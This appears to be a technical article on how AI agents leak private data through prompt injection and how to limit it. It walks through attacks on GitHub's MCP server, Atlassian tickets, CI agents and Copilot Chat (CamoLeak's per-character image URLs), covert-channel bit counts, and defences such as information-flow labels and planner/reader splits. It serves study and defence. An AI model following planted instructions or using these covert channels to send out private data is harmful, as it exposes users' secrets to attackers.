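The pull request revealed the name of a private project, as well as the owner's salary and plan to move to South America. Every tool worked as its developers intended, and the agent contacted only GitHub's servers.

Claude Desktop asks the user to approve each tool call by default, but many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. A request to read a repository looks routine, so the important approval for this kind of leak is the one for the pull request, whose text contained the owner's salary. An owner who read that text before approving it would probably have stopped the attack.

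Invariant Labs recommends allowing only one repository per session. A program between the agent and GitHub records the first repository the agent uses and blocks calls to any other. With this rule, the agent in the demonstration would still have read the planted issue but could not have opened the private repositories. Invariant Labs sells software that enforces such rules, but this one is simple enough for firms to write themselves. The rule also blocks legitimate work across repositories, such as copying a fix from one to another. It covers only GitHub, so if the agent can also read the owner's mailbox in the same session, it can still copy a salary from an email into the public repository.

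According to Invariant Labs, GitHub can't solve the problem by changing its server. That is true of prompt injection in general, but GitHub has since added server settings that would block this particular attack.

**Scanning for credentials.** In August, GitHub (2025) announced that its server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for tokens, keys and credentials. The feature is on by default, but users can bypass a block. It wouldn't have stopped this leak, because a salary or a travel plan doesn't look like a key, and neither does a six-digit courier code.

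**Lockdown mode.** In December, GitHub (2025) introduced a setting that hides content in public repositories from the agent unless its author has push access, meaning permission to change the code. With the setting on, the planted issue would have produced an error instead of reaching the model. Users have to turn it on themselves, and it prevents the agent from sorting bug reports submitted by the public, which is one of the main reasons to connect it. GitLab's *CVE-2026-48529* (2026) records a flaw in lockdown mode on servers that several people share. The server used the first user's credentials for every user's lockdown queries. Firms that run a shared server should check their version against that advisory.

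Classmethod's *Use GitHub MCP in Read-only mode* (2026) explains how to use the server without giving the agent write permission, so the agent can't open a pull request. This is a good choice for someone who only wants summaries of issues.

An owner who needs the agent to write can give it an access token that works only for the game's repository. The agent can open pull requests and read strangers' issues there, but GitHub blocks its access to the private repositories. This is less convenient than one token for everything, but it doesn't depend on the model's behavior or on anybody reading approval requests.

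### Agents that start on their own

In the Pac-Man attack, the owner had to ask about the issues first. Many projects instead start agents automatically through GitHub Actions, a service that runs programs when something happens in a repository. Opening a pull request can be enough to start an agent.

SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* describes attacks on these three agents that security engineer Aonan Guan and two Johns Hopkins University researchers disclosed in April 2026. In Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, instructions in a pull request's title made the agent run commands, collect credentials and report them as a security finding. According to Techzine, the finding appeared as a comment on the pull request and contained an Anthropic key and a GitHub token. The credentials could also appear in the job's log, which should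 be treated as public if the project is public.

Google's Gemini CLI Action leaked a complete API key. GitHub's Copilot agent also leaked data, although a person first had to assign the attacker's issue to it. Copilot's network firewall didn't prevent the leak because it has to let the agent reach GitHub, where the attacker reads the result.

The vendors' responses have been limited. Anthropic blocked one command, `ps`, which lists running programs. Guan thinks the attack still works in principle if the attacker rewrites the text, but he did not attempt a full bypass. Google added warnings to the agent's prompt and left its tools unchanged. GitHub called the problem a known limitation of the design. Projects that use such agents shouldn't rely on these fixes. They can require a maintainer to start the agent when a stranger opens a pull request and keep keys out of the environment where the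 agent runs commands.

### A support ticket that answered its author

The destination doesn't have to be public. Jira Service Management is an Atlassian product through which a company's customers submit support tickets. In May 2025 Atlassian released an MCP server that connects agents to its products. On 19 June, Waizel, Attiya and Bamberger (2025), in *PoC Attack Targeting Atlassian’s Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, showed how a customer could use it to read a company's internal data:

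1. The attacker submitted a support ticket containing planted instructions.
2. A support engineer processed the ticket with Claude Sonnet, which had access to Atlassian's products through the MCP server.
3. The agent followed the instructions with the engineer's permissions and collected internal data that customers can't see.
4. The agent wrote the data into the ticket.
5. The attacker opened the ticket and read it.

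The attacker never had access to the MCP server and only needed to read their own ticket, which the company allows every customer to do. The researchers, at the security company Cato Networks, also found many companies' ticket portals with an ordinary web search. Possible targets are therefore easy to find, but a portal doesn't show whether the company's staff use an agent to handle tickets. Neither Cato Networks nor Invariant Labs gives a success rate, so their demonstrations show that the data can get out but not how often an attempt would work.

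Atlassian promised in its announcement that the server would keep data secure and within users' permissions (quoted in Willison, 2025). The attack stayed within those permissions. The engineer was allowed to read the internal data and to write in the ticket, so a system that checks each call separately would allow both, even though together they leak the data.

Waizel and colleagues suggest a rule that either blocks tool calls that create, add or edit anything, or raises an alert about them. Blocking them works but leaves the engineer to write every reply. An alert is weaker, because the customer may have received the reply by email before anybody sees the alert. It would be better to hold each reply until the engineer has read its exact text and knows the customer will see it.

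In a note to customers, Atlassian says using agents with its products through MCP is the customer's choice. It recommends giving an agent as little access as possible, requiring clear approval before any change to data, and logging what the agent does. This is sensible advice, but it leaves each company responsible for preventing the attack. The router firm already has the safest arrangement for tickets, because a person writes each reply.

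### Private projects and shared documents

People often overlook that an attacker may be one of the permitted readers of a private project. Underhill (2026), in *Azure DevOps Prompt Injection Targets AI Coding Agents*, describes an attack on Microsoft's service for managing software projects. The attacker had access to one project and planted instructions there. A developer's agent followed them, used the developer's wider permissions to read another project's wiki, and posted the text to the attacker's pull request. The wiki text would leak even if both projects were private, because different people can read each one.

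An agent editing a shared document can leak private information through the text it leaves in place as well as the text it adds. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) tested attacks in which the attacker talks to someone's personal agent and invites it to work on a Notion page. In one attack, the page has a blank section for the agent to complete, and the agent fills it with private information because it treats the task as collaboration. In another, the attacker lists true and false claims about a person and asks the agent to clean up the page. The agent refuses to delete the true claims, so the attacker can tell which ones are true even though the agent hasn't written anything private.

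The researchers tested these attacks, and one that asks for data in one channel and collects it in another, on an agent whose prompt required it to get consent before sharing anything. The new attacks obtained 43.8% to 75.6% of the private items, compared with 1.9% to 3.0% for the attacks used to develop the prompt. In a test with live Gmail and Notion accounts and a different defence, the clean-up attack obtained 34.7%. All these attackers made ordinary requests and planted no hidden instructions, so the percentages don't measure prompt injection. But an attacker who can plant instructions could ask for the same edits, and the result would appear on the same page.

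### How often models leak through arguments and answers

Huang and colleagues used CIPL, the framework that separates private data an agent uses from data an attacker recovers, to test four small agent systems. Two retrieved records from a memory of 200 past interactions, one to answer questions about medical records and the other to do tasks on the web. A third answered questions from a store of five documents. The fourth used a tool to work with five private records, and the attacker could see either the tool's arguments or a tool result that the agent repeated.

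The researchers tested each system with five models. They sent 30 attack queries per run and repeated the run with five random seeds. Their any-leak rate is the share of queries that revealed at least one private item. They also ran the tool tests with queries that kept the task but left out cues to extract data, such as a request for exact wording or raw output.

| Model | Arguments, with cues | Repeated results, with cues | Arguments, without cues | Repeated results, without cues |
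|---|---|---|---|---|
| MiniMax-M2.5 | 0.28 | 0.37 | 0.03 | 0.07 |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 0.27 | 0.37 | 0.01 | 0.01 |
| qwen3.5-plus | 0.31 | 0.40 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek | 1.00 | 1.00 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-4o | 0.99 | 1.00 | 0 | 0.02 |

The leak rate depended much more on the model than on the channel. Three models leaked somewhat more often through repeated results than through arguments, while the other two leaked almost every time through both. The average for arguments on qwen3.5-plus is very uncertain because it was smaller than its standard deviation across the five seeds, 0.35. Although GPT-4o's leak rates for the two channels were nearly identical, at 0.99 and 1.00, it revealed everything it had looked up in all the trials with repeated results but in only 49% of those with arguments.

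Both memory systems leaked all the retrieved records in every trial, on every model. The document system leaked something in 80% to 98% of trials, but leaked everything in at most 21%. The low rate of complete leaks was due to the queries used, because when the researchers switched to a crude request to dump the contents, the three models they tried revealed everything in 92% to 100% of trials.

Adding an instruction to the prompt to withhold private data reduced leakage, but a lot remained. On GPT-4o, the any-leak rate fell from 1.00 to 0.20 for repeated results and from 0.99 to 0.46 for arguments. Those rates are still high enough for an attacker who can send 30 queries.

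Huang and colleagues also read 200 of the outputs by hand. Half contained a leak, and the software had found no exact match in 12 of those 100. In one of the 12, the model printed word for word the secret phrase for approving a wire transfer, but the software missed it because it searched only for the whole record. Searching for the phrase itself would have caught that leak. Detecting a paraphrased leak takes a human reader or a second model.

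These rates don't apply to an agent that reads a malicious web page, because the attacker in CIPL is the person using the agent. The model has good reason to follow that person's requests, whereas instructions on a web page compete with them. This suggests that planted text would cause leaks less often, but attackers can tune it to a particular agent, which the researchers didn't try to do. The tool tests also used only five records and looked up two at a time, far fewer than a real mailbox holds. The near-zero rates without cues show that ordinary requests seldom caused leaks in this setup, but they are weak evidence of how the models would respond to planted text.

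### Checks for each destination and tool

1. **Find out who can read each destination.** Open it from an account with no special rights, then as a customer or guest if such accounts exist. Include notification emails, job logs and edit histories. Deleting a secret from a file in a repository doesn't remove it from earlier commits.
2. **Find out whether a write is public by default.** Have the agent post a harmless sentence without choosing who can see it, and look for it from an outsider's account. Many ticket systems offer both internal notes and replies to the customer. If the tool lets the model choose between them, set the choice in the tool's code instead.
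3. **List what one session can read and where it can write.** For each source and destination, ask whether everyone who can read the destination may also read the source. If not, use separate sessions with separate credentials. Starting a new chat isn't enough if the agent keeps a memory between chats or the same token opens both.
4. **Ask each tool provider what it logs.** Find out whether it stores complete arguments, including those of failed calls, how long it keeps them and who can read them. If the provider can't answer, assume that it keeps everything. Record the agent's calls for a day as well, because the arguments often contain more than the task needs.
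5. **Require approval for writes that outsiders can read.** Show the complete text and its readers on the same screen, and turn off "Always Allow" for these writes.

The router firm's tracker fails the third check because the agent writes to it while the courier code is in the agent's context. Until the firm keeps the code separate from the agent's writing to the tracker, an employee can approve each bug report before the agent posts it. The employee would notice the code 482913 in the text, but probably not a code spread across the agent's choice of labels and wording.

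## Calculating how much a permitted action can reveal

The employee who approves the router firm's bug reports looks for private text, and so does a filter. Neither helps if the secret determines which of several harmless actions the agent takes. For example, an attacker could have 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, so that the page the agent opens reveals a character of the secret.

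Inspecting requests one at a time will not catch this, but an engineer can still calculate the most that such choices could reveal by counting the different things the attacker might see.

### One choice among N addresses

The amount of information an action can reveal is measured in bits. One bit distinguishes two equally likely possibilities, and each further bit doubles that number, so a choice among N equally likely possibilities carries log₂ N bits. Choosing one of 36 pages carries 5.17 bits. A six-digit code such as the firm's courier code has a million possible values, so it contains 19.93 bits.

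*Model Counting Modulo Theories* (2015) proves that a program with N possible outputs can leak at most log₂ N bits about a secret. An attacker can't learn more about the secret than the uncertainty about the output before seeing it, which is at most log₂ N bits. The leak reaches this maximum only if the secret alone determines the output and all N outputs are equally likely.

The average number of bits leaked can be a poor guide to how easily an attacker will guess a secret. *Algebraic Foundations for Information Theoretical, Probabilistic and Guessability measures of Information Flow* (2011) explains that the same maximum applies to a measure based on the attacker's chance of guessing right at the first attempt. If a secret has M equally likely values and the attacker sees one of N possible results, that chance is at most N/M. If the secret has a million values, a request to one of 36 pages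 can raise the chance from one in a million to 36 in a million.

The count must include everything the attacker can observe, including the agent opening no page. An agent that may open one of the 36 pages or none therefore has 37 options and can reveal up to 5.21 bits. An agent that may open only one fixed page can still reveal one bit, because it can choose whether to open it. If it opens that page on every job, whatever the secret, it has only one option and reveals nothing.

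The timing of a request can reveal more than the choice of page. A web server's log records the time to the second, so a request that could come at any second in ten minutes has 600 possible times and can reveal up to 9.2 bits through timing alone. The figures below assume that timing reveals nothing, for instance because a proxy sends requests only at fixed times.

### Several requests

If the agent makes k requests, each to one of N pages, and the attacker sees their order, there are Nᵏ possible sequences, which can reveal at most k log₂ N bits. With 36 pages, three requests give 46,656 sequences, too few to assign a different one to each of a million codes. Four requests give 1,679,616, which is enough.

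The attacker sees less if order is hidden and each page can appear only once. The attacker then sees only which k of the N pages were opened, and there are C(N, k) = N! / (k! (N − k)!) such sets. Kovačević and Vukobratović (2012), in *Subset Codes for Packet Networks*, studied the same problem in networks that deliver packets in an unpredictable order. They represent each set as a string of N bits, with a one for each item in the set. So 36 pages can carry at most 36 bits in a session, even if the agent may open any number of them.

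The table applies the formulas to 36 pages. The number of bits is log₂ of the number of possible observations.

| What the attacker sees | Possible observations | Bits in four requests | Requests needed for a six-digit code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Order and repeats | Nᵏ | 20.7 | 4 |
| Order, but no page twice | N! / (N − k)! | 20.4 | 4 |
| How often the agent opened each page, without order | C(N + k − 1, k) | 16.3 | 6 |
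| Only which k pages the agent opened | C(N, k) | 15.8 | 6 |

Hiding the order makes the attacker use two more requests. Blocking repeats makes almost no difference to a secret this short.

An attacker can leak more data when there are more pages to request. With 1,000 pages and a limit of five distinct requests in hidden order, the attacker can leak at most log₂ C(1000, 5), or about 43 bits, which is more than twice the information in the courier code. If the order is visible, two requests are enough, because 1,000 × 1,000 gives exactly one million sequences, one for each possible code.

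### CamoLeak

An attack on GitHub Copilot Chat, the AI assistant on GitHub's website, used choices of this kind to steal much more than six digits. GitHub's Content Security Policy blocked images from loading directly from outside servers. They could load only through GitHub's proxy, Camo, which accepted only addresses that GitHub had signed.

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how its researcher got past this in June 2025:

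1. The attacker had GitHub sign an address for each character in advance. All the addresses led to the attacker's server.
2. The attacker put these addresses and some instructions into a pull request, inside a comment that GitHub hides from readers.
3. Another user opened the pull request and asked Copilot about it. Copilot worked with that user's permissions, so it could read their private repositories.
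4. The answer contained a row of invisible images that spelled out private text. The browser requested them through Camo, and the attacker read the text from the order of requests.

The researcher obtained the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search a user's code for cloud access keys and send out the result. Every address was genuine and signed, and none contained any of the stolen text.

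Caching didn't hide repeated characters, because Camo accepted a signed address with an extra part on the end. The model changed that part each time, so each repeat looked like a new image. To prevent this, a cache has to treat such variants as the same address or reject them.

GitHub fixed the flaw by 14 August 2025. Legit Security reports that GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat, while SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* describes the fix more narrowly, as a ban on using Camo to leak user data. Turning off images reduces this route to zero bits, because no answer then triggers an image request. Turning them off doesn't by itself affect links, which the researcher had also used to get private data out when a user clicked.

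### Caching and blocking repeat visits

Rehberger proposes either caching pages for a few minutes or forbidding a second visit in the same session. Both keep an attacker from seeing repeat visits to a page. As the table shows, this reduces the information an attacker who wants a six-digit code can get from four requests by only a quarter of a bit.

The proposals are more useful for long secrets, because the attacker runs out of pages. Opening all 36 pages in a chosen order can reveal log₂(36!), or about 138 bits, and the option to stop early adds only one or two more. A random 40-character key with 64 possibilities per character holds 240 bits. An attacker could leak the whole key in 47 requests if repeats were allowed, but blocking repeats makes this impossible in one session.

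That protection disappears if the attacker has more pages, because a full ordering of 1,000 pages carries about 8,500 bits. Rehberger acknowledges in Embrace The Red that his proposals would still allow some leakage.

A ban for the whole session is better than a short cache. With a five-minute cache, the attacker can see each page once every five minutes. An agent that works for half an hour has six such periods, so even with the order hidden, 36 pages could carry 6 × 36 = 216 bits.

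Hiding the order as well reduces the maximum from 138 bits to 36. A proxy can do this by collecting requests and sending them together in random order. That works for images in a finished answer but not for an agent that reads one page before choosing the next. It also doesn't stop an attacker who prepares separate addresses for each position, much as packet networks number packets so the receiver can put them back in order. ZombieAgent did this, and its ten requests carried about 52 bits without repeating an address or needing to arrive in order.

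Blocking some of the attacker's addresses does little to limit a leak. When Rehberger tested OpenAI's first image check in December 2023, nine of his 36 single-character addresses passed. Blocking the other three quarters reduced what each request could reveal from 5.17 bits to 3.17, so an attacker would need seven ordered requests instead of four to leak a six-digit code. Rehberger also suggested allowing only one image per answer, or a handful at most. This would work better, because halving the number of ordered requests halves the total number of bits that can leak, while halving the number of addresses removes only one bit per request.

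The strictest form of caching serves only stored copies, so this route leaks zero bits. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode does this for browsing, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. Users lose a lot of functionality, since some search results may be missing and Deep Research and agent mode are off. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* document warns that connected apps can still leak data and that the setting doesn't affect Codex's network access.

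### Noise and mistakes

Real attacks usually leak less than the maximum because caches hide requests, other visitors add their own, and the model sometimes picks the wrong page. A counter that either rises or doesn't could carry one bit per run. The download counter described earlier, which goes up in 40% of runs for an even first digit and 30% for an odd one, carries only about 0.008 bits per run.

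In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) measured such losses in an attack that doesn't ask the agent to leak anything. A link on an ordinary page leads to the attacker's site, which offers four references on different subjects. The agent opens the one that suits its task, which reveals something about what the user asked. The researchers also tried signalling the same four-way choice in other ways, such as by the number or timing of requests.

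A choice among four options can carry at most two bits. The estimates in the last column below assume that the options are equally likely and that the attacker's wrong readings are spread evenly among them.

| Signal | Trials with a signal | Correct readings among those | Estimated bits, out of 2 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which page the agent opens | 98.7% | 93.8% | 1.5 |
| Request or no request | 95.8% | 89.6% | 1.3 |
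| Number of requests | 90.2% | 73.5% | 0.7 |
| Order of requests | 94.1% | 67.9% | 0.6 |
| Timing | 87.3% | 58.6% | 0.3 |
| Amount of data transferred | 41.5% | 62.4% | 0.2 |

Leaking data through the choice of page took only one request, while leaking it through whether the agent made a request took two on average. Timing performed far worse than its theoretical capacity suggests, but it may still be useful to an attacker who can repeat the attempt.

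Offering more options did not help this attacker. With 16 clearly different references, accuracy fell to 50%, so by the same estimate one choice reveals about 1 of a possible 4 bits, less than a choice among four references. The attacker did better by asking a series of narrower questions. With four levels of detail, this recovered the right answer 49% of the time, compared with 14% for asking about everything at once.

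Across 500 questions from Stack Exchange, the full attack needed about 6.5 probes per question. It recovered the concepts in the question with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means that the attacker found every concept and added no wrong ones. When the researchers replaced the agent's choices with random ones in one setup, the score fell from 0.81 to 0.10, which shows that the information came from the choices and not from lucky guesses by the attacker's model.

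Four existing defences lowered the scores by at most 0.03. One was Fides, the system by Costa and colleagues whose guarantee doesn't cover what an outsider can infer from an agent's choice of action. The experiment made the attacker's task easier, though, by adding the link to 2,600 pages that the agents tended to visit early. The scores also exclude the roughly 6% of attempts on these questions that produced no readable path.

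These error rates don't carry over to an attack like CamoLeak. Liang and colleagues' attacker relied on the agent to judge which reference was relevant, and more than one can be. A planted table that assigns one address to each character removes that ambiguity. An attacker can also use redundancy to correct errors. Kovačević and Vukobratović prove, for example, that if any two sets in the attacker's code differ by at least five items, the receiver can work out the right set even when two items are missing.

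A designer should base the limit on the theoretical maximum, because noise that nobody controls may disappear when the vendor installs a better model.

### Repeated sessions

A limit of five requests per session doesn't cap the total number of requests about one secret, because an attacker can use many sessions. If each session can reveal B bits and the secret stays the same, n sessions can reveal up to n × B bits. An attacker who learns only one bit from each ticket can ask about a different part of the courier code each time and have all of it after 20 tickets, without any single ticket looking unusual. Twenty bits are enough to distinguish 2²⁰ codes, or just over a million.

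Liang and colleagues' attack stored its progress on the attacker's server, so starting a new chat would not have erased what the attacker had learned. If the agent returned, the attack continued from the last confirmed answer and repeated or broadened any question that had failed.

Some designs leak much more slowly than others over time. *Quantifying information flow in interactive systems* (2019) proves that in a class of deterministic systems, the total leak grows either in proportion to time or only with its logarithm, and calls the two cases "dangerous" and "safe". If an agent may contact the attacker's site once a day, its daily choice between a request and silence can carry 365 bits over a year. If it may contact the site only once all year, the attacker learns at most which day it did so, or that it never did, which is about 8.5 bits. Allowing one request over two years instead would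 add only about one bit.

Even a "safe" action can leak a whole secret if the secret is a yes or no, such as whether a shop suspects a customer of fraud or whether a company will buy a competitor, because one bit is enough to reveal it. If the agent opens a page only when the answer is yes, the attacker learns the answer from whether the request arrives. Averages can hide this risk when one answer is rare. If one patient in a hundred has a certain illness, whether a patient has it carries only 0.08 bits of information on average, far below any practical limit, but a single request can still expose a patient who does.

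A single action can also answer several yes-or-no questions. In the clean-up attack by Shim and colleagues, each claim that the agent refuses to delete is probably true. One edit to a page with ten claims can therefore reveal ten bits, so limiting the number of edits would not help.

### Choosing a limit

A request limit should start from the secret and how long it stays valid.

1. Count the secret's possible values, M. If some are much more likely than others, as with birthdays or common passwords, assume that the attacker tries those first.
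2. Decide what chance of a correct guess is acceptable, and how many guesses the attacker gets before somebody blocks them.
3. Count what the attacker could see in one job, including silence, and multiply the counts for all jobs before the secret changes.
4. Divide that total by M and multiply by the number of guesses. The result is the attacker's maximum chance of success if all values are equally likely, and anything above 1 means that the limit gives no protection.

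Suppose the router firm changes its courier code weekly and accepts at most a 1 in 1,000 chance that an attacker guesses it in one try. With 36 pages, one visible request per week gives 37 possible observations and a 37 in a million chance of a correct guess. Two requests give 37² = 1,369 possible observations and a chance of about 1.4 in 1,000, which is too high. A support agent that can open only one outside page a week is useless, so a request limit can't protect this code. The firm has to keep the code away from the agent that fetches pages, or give that agent only stored copies of pages.

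Limits work much better for long random keys. If 100 bits of a 240-bit key leak, the remaining 140 are far too many to guess. A 100-bit limit would allow 19 visible requests among 36 pages over the key's lifetime, or ten among 1,000. But the same 100 bits could encode 19 characters from a document, enough for a person's name.

A program can enforce such a limit with a budget. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes a monitor that keeps a budget of bits for each destination, deducts an estimate of the bits each suspicious message could reveal, and refills the budget over time. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or blocks further messages. Metere doesn't try to prevent every leak, because an agent can always reveal one bit by either sending a message or not sending it.

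To protect a particular secret, the firm should apply one allowance to all destinations combined, because an attacker who controls several would otherwise get several allowances. The allowance should also refill only when the secret changes. A refill of ten bits a day would let out 70 bits in a week, more than three times enough to reveal the courier code. However, an attacker can deliberately use up any shared allowance and stop the agent from fetching pages for honest customers.

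Another option is to make the requests independent of the secret. If the agent always opens all 36 pages, C(36, 36) = 1, and the choice carries no information. Liang and colleagues used this idea in a defence that downloads every resource linked from a page, whatever the user asked, and lets the agent choose among the local copies. On the Stack Exchange questions, the attacker still found 91% of the true concepts, but the share of guesses that were correct fell from 87% to 29%. The agent made 4.3 times as many page requests. Some leakage can remain when the agent needs something outside the local copies, because the defence only mixes that request with random ones.

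The same counting applies to what the agent writes. If the firm's tracker has 20 labels and the agent may attach any combination, it can label one harmless bug report in 2²⁰ ways, enough to reveal the whole courier code. Allowing at most one label leaves 21 possibilities, or 4.4 bits. If an employee chooses the label without seeing the agent's suggestion, the agent can't leak anything through the label, but the wording of the report can still carry far more than 4.4 bits.

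## Keeping private data apart from outward actions

The dependable way to keep the courier code out of a bug report is to ensure that whatever writes the report has never read the code. This works even if the model follows every planted instruction, so nobody has to recognise an attack.

### Removing one of the three conditions

This kind of theft needs private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out, so a designer can prevent it by removing any one of them. For the router firm, the private data is the easiest to remove. The model doesn't need the code's six digits, because it only has to state that the firm owes the customer a free return. The console can show the code beside the summary when a member of staff opens it. If the code never enters the agent's context, no label, page request or wording can depend on it. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* applies the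 same reasoning to credentials such as passwords. If they never enter the sandbox, the closed environment where an agent runs its commands, they can't leak from it, whether the cause is an attacker, a careless user or the model itself.

Dana's mailbox supplies two of the three conditions, so her assistant must not have the third, a way to send data out. An assistant with no fetch tool, whose client loads no images and shows no links, can still summarise her mail and answer questions about it. If she also wants to use the web, she can open a separate session that has no access to her mail. She then has to copy facts between the two sessions herself, such as the date she bought something.

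Willison thinks that people who combine tools from different makers have no other safe option, because no single vendor controls the combination.

### A planner and a reader

Some jobs need all three conditions at once. Suppose a user asks an agent to find the notes of a meeting and send a summary to a colleague. In 2023 Willison proposed splitting such an agent into two models, an idea known as the dual-LLM pattern. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, use a job like this one to explain it:

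1. The planner, a model with access to the tools, reads only the user's request. It decides to find the notes, have them summarised and send the summary to the colleague.
2. The program around the models fetches the notes and stores them under a name such as `notes_1`. The planner sees the name but not the text.
3. The reader, a model without tools, receives the notes and returns a summary, which the program stores as `summary_1`.
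4. The planner asks the program to send `summary_1` to the colleague, and the program fills in the text.

Instructions hidden in the notes can reach only the reader, which can't send or fetch anything. They can still make the summary wrong. If the plan takes the colleague's address from the notes, they can also supply the attacker's address instead, and the agent would then send the summary to the attacker while following the planner's steps exactly.

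*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) gives an idea of how many attacks the split stops. It examines the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark that combines ordinary agent tasks with planted attacks. In 97 of 144 task-attack combinations, the attack needed a tool call or file that a plan for the user's task would never include. In the other 47, the attack could succeed within a normal plan.

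A planner can also undo the protection. In one task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. Garby and colleagues twice saw a planner respond by writing a loop that turned whatever the file contained into tool calls, so the file's author decided which calls the agent made.

The split makes some tasks difficult, because the planner can't react to text it hasn't read. Costa and colleagues give the example of checking three emails for a meeting request and adding any meeting to the calendar. In their solution, the reader may give the planner only a yes or no answer. If the answer is yes, the reader extracts the details into a variable, which goes to the calendar without the planner seeing its contents. A planted email could cause a wrong answer, but a single yes or no can't contain new instructions.

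By one count, the right actions depend on what the agent reads in about 43% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks, but in only 5% of its office tasks. A firm should therefore check its own tasks before deciding whether it can keep private data apart from outward actions.

### Trust labels and reader labels

Information-flow control deals with the attacker's address in the meeting notes by having the program label every piece of data and check the labels before each action. The trust label records whether an outsider could have written or altered the data, and the reader label lists who may see it.

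When the agent combines data, the program also combines the labels, always in the cautious direction. Anything based partly on untrusted text is untrusted. Only people who may read all of the sources may read the result. If A, B and C may read a sales plan and B, C and D may read a price list, only B and C may read a summary of both:

```
{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}
```

Nobody can reliably tell which parts of its context a model used, so Costa and colleagues give its output the combined label of everything in the context. Before a tool call, the program can apply two rules:

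- **Trust rule:** the agent may act only if everything that influenced the decision is trusted.
- **Reader rule:** data may go to a recipient only if the recipient is on its reader label.

A strict policy requires both, while a looser one accepts either. Under the looser policy, private data may go to someone new as long as no untrusted text influenced the action. Dana could then tell her assistant to email her address to a plumber, but a stranger's message could not make the assistant send it.

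Suppose Dana's assistant uses the strict policy and someone has sent her a malicious email. As in the tests by Costa and colleagues, an email's readers are its sender and recipients.

| Step | What happens | Label of the new text | Label of the whole context |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Dana asks whether she can return her last order | Trusted, anyone | Trusted, anyone |
| 2 | The assistant reads the shop's confirmation of order 70415 | Untrusted, Dana and the shop | Untrusted, Dana and the shop |
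| 3 | It reads the attacker's email, which contains planted instructions | Untrusted, Dana and the attacker | Untrusted, only Dana |
| 4 | The model asks to fetch an address at pics.example.net with the order number in it | Same as the context | Unchanged |

At step 4 the program compares the label of the address with the destination. The context is untrusted, so the request fails the trust rule. The owner of pics.example.net isn't Dana, so the request also fails the reader rule. The program refuses the request before looking up the server's name, so nothing appears in the attacker's log.

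The program refused the address because the model had chosen it after reading private text. It never searched the address for 70415, so it would also have refused an address that contained the number in encoded form or contained no private data.

The same caution also blocks harmless requests. After step 2, a request to the shop's own website would have passed the reader rule, since the shop already knows the order number. After step 3, the same request fails because the attacker's email has removed the shop from the list of permitted readers. One irrelevant message can therefore stop the assistant from finishing a legitimate task.

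### Fides, CaMeL and FLOWSH

Three systems apply these ideas in different ways. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built Fides in 2025, and researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich built CaMeL the same year. Kim and colleagues introduced FLOWSH, the shell, in November 2026. The completion figures come from each system's designers, except that Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL. The tests used different tasks and models, so the figures can't be used to rank the systems.

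| | Fides | CaMeL | FLOWSH |
|---|---|---|---|
| Guarantee | Private data doesn't flow directly into an action that the policy forbids | Outside text can't add steps to the plan, and every tool call satisfies that tool's rule | Network requests and file changes that break the policy don't take effect without approval |
| Observer | Someone who sees the public data that tools write | Someone who receives data from a tool call | Owner of a server that a command contacts |
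| Left out | Order of tool calls, timing and packet length | Some leaks through branches and retries | Private data sent when everything the agent has read is trusted |
| Completed tasks | 50%, against 84% without protection | 18 of 48 banking runs, about half as many as with its rules off | 88% of office-type tasks with a perfect approver and 59% with none, against 96% and 94% without label checks |

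**Fides** reduces the problem of the irrelevant email by hiding text from the planner. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the context, the program stores the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The context keeps its old label, so the agent can still act. In AgentDojo, 152 planted attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent without label checks, and none succeeded with them.

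The 50% in the table is the average over AgentDojo's four environments with GPT-4o. An agent that applied the same rules without hiding anything scored 42%. The lead grew from 8 to 16 points with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model that made better use of the variables. Both models are old, so the loss in completed tasks may well be smaller today. The tests also left out the restricted yes-or-no answers, which might have let the agent complete a few more tasks.

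In **CaMeL**, the planner writes the whole plan as a short program in restricted Python before anything reads outside text. An interpreter then runs the plan, calls the tools and stores the reader's answers with labels attached (*CaMeLoT*, 2026). Planted text can influence which of the plan's branches the interpreter follows, but it can't add a branch.

Each label records where a value came from and who may receive it, and each tool has its own rule, written by hand. *SPA* (2026) points out that such rules can express more than a simple comparison of labels, but the guarantee then depends on every rule being correct and complete. Garby and colleagues add that CaMeL's tracking has not been proven to catch every leak.

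In a rerun, CaMeL blocked every attack when its rules were on. The rules also stopped it from completing many tasks, but some of those should fail, because paying whatever bill an untrusted file contains, for example, is unsafe under any policy. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) presents a system that lets the model that reads untrusted text use tools, and relies on labels to restrict what it does afterwards. That system still completed only 8 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with its rules on, down from 15 without them, and CaMeL completed 7. An agent could recover some of the unsafe tasks by asking the user about them.

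**FLOWSH** applies labels to shell commands, which are harder to check than an email tool because a single command can start other programs and read files that don't appear in its text. It runs each command in a sandbox, records which files the command opens and which servers it contacts, and combines their labels with the command's own. File labels stay on disk with the files, so a secret that the agent saves in one session is still labeled secret when a later session reads it.

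Kim and colleagues tested it with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office-type tasks, the 89 command-line tasks in the Terminal-Bench benchmark, and 19 attack cases, running everything three times. No attack succeeded, even when the attacker controlled the model's output.

Compared with a "Lax" sandbox that permits everything but asks for approval before every shell command, FLOWSH needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed office task and 22.5 times fewer on Terminal-Bench. Its completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower on office tasks and 9.7 points lower on Terminal-Bench. It also took 17% to 34% longer and used 17% to 55% more tokens.

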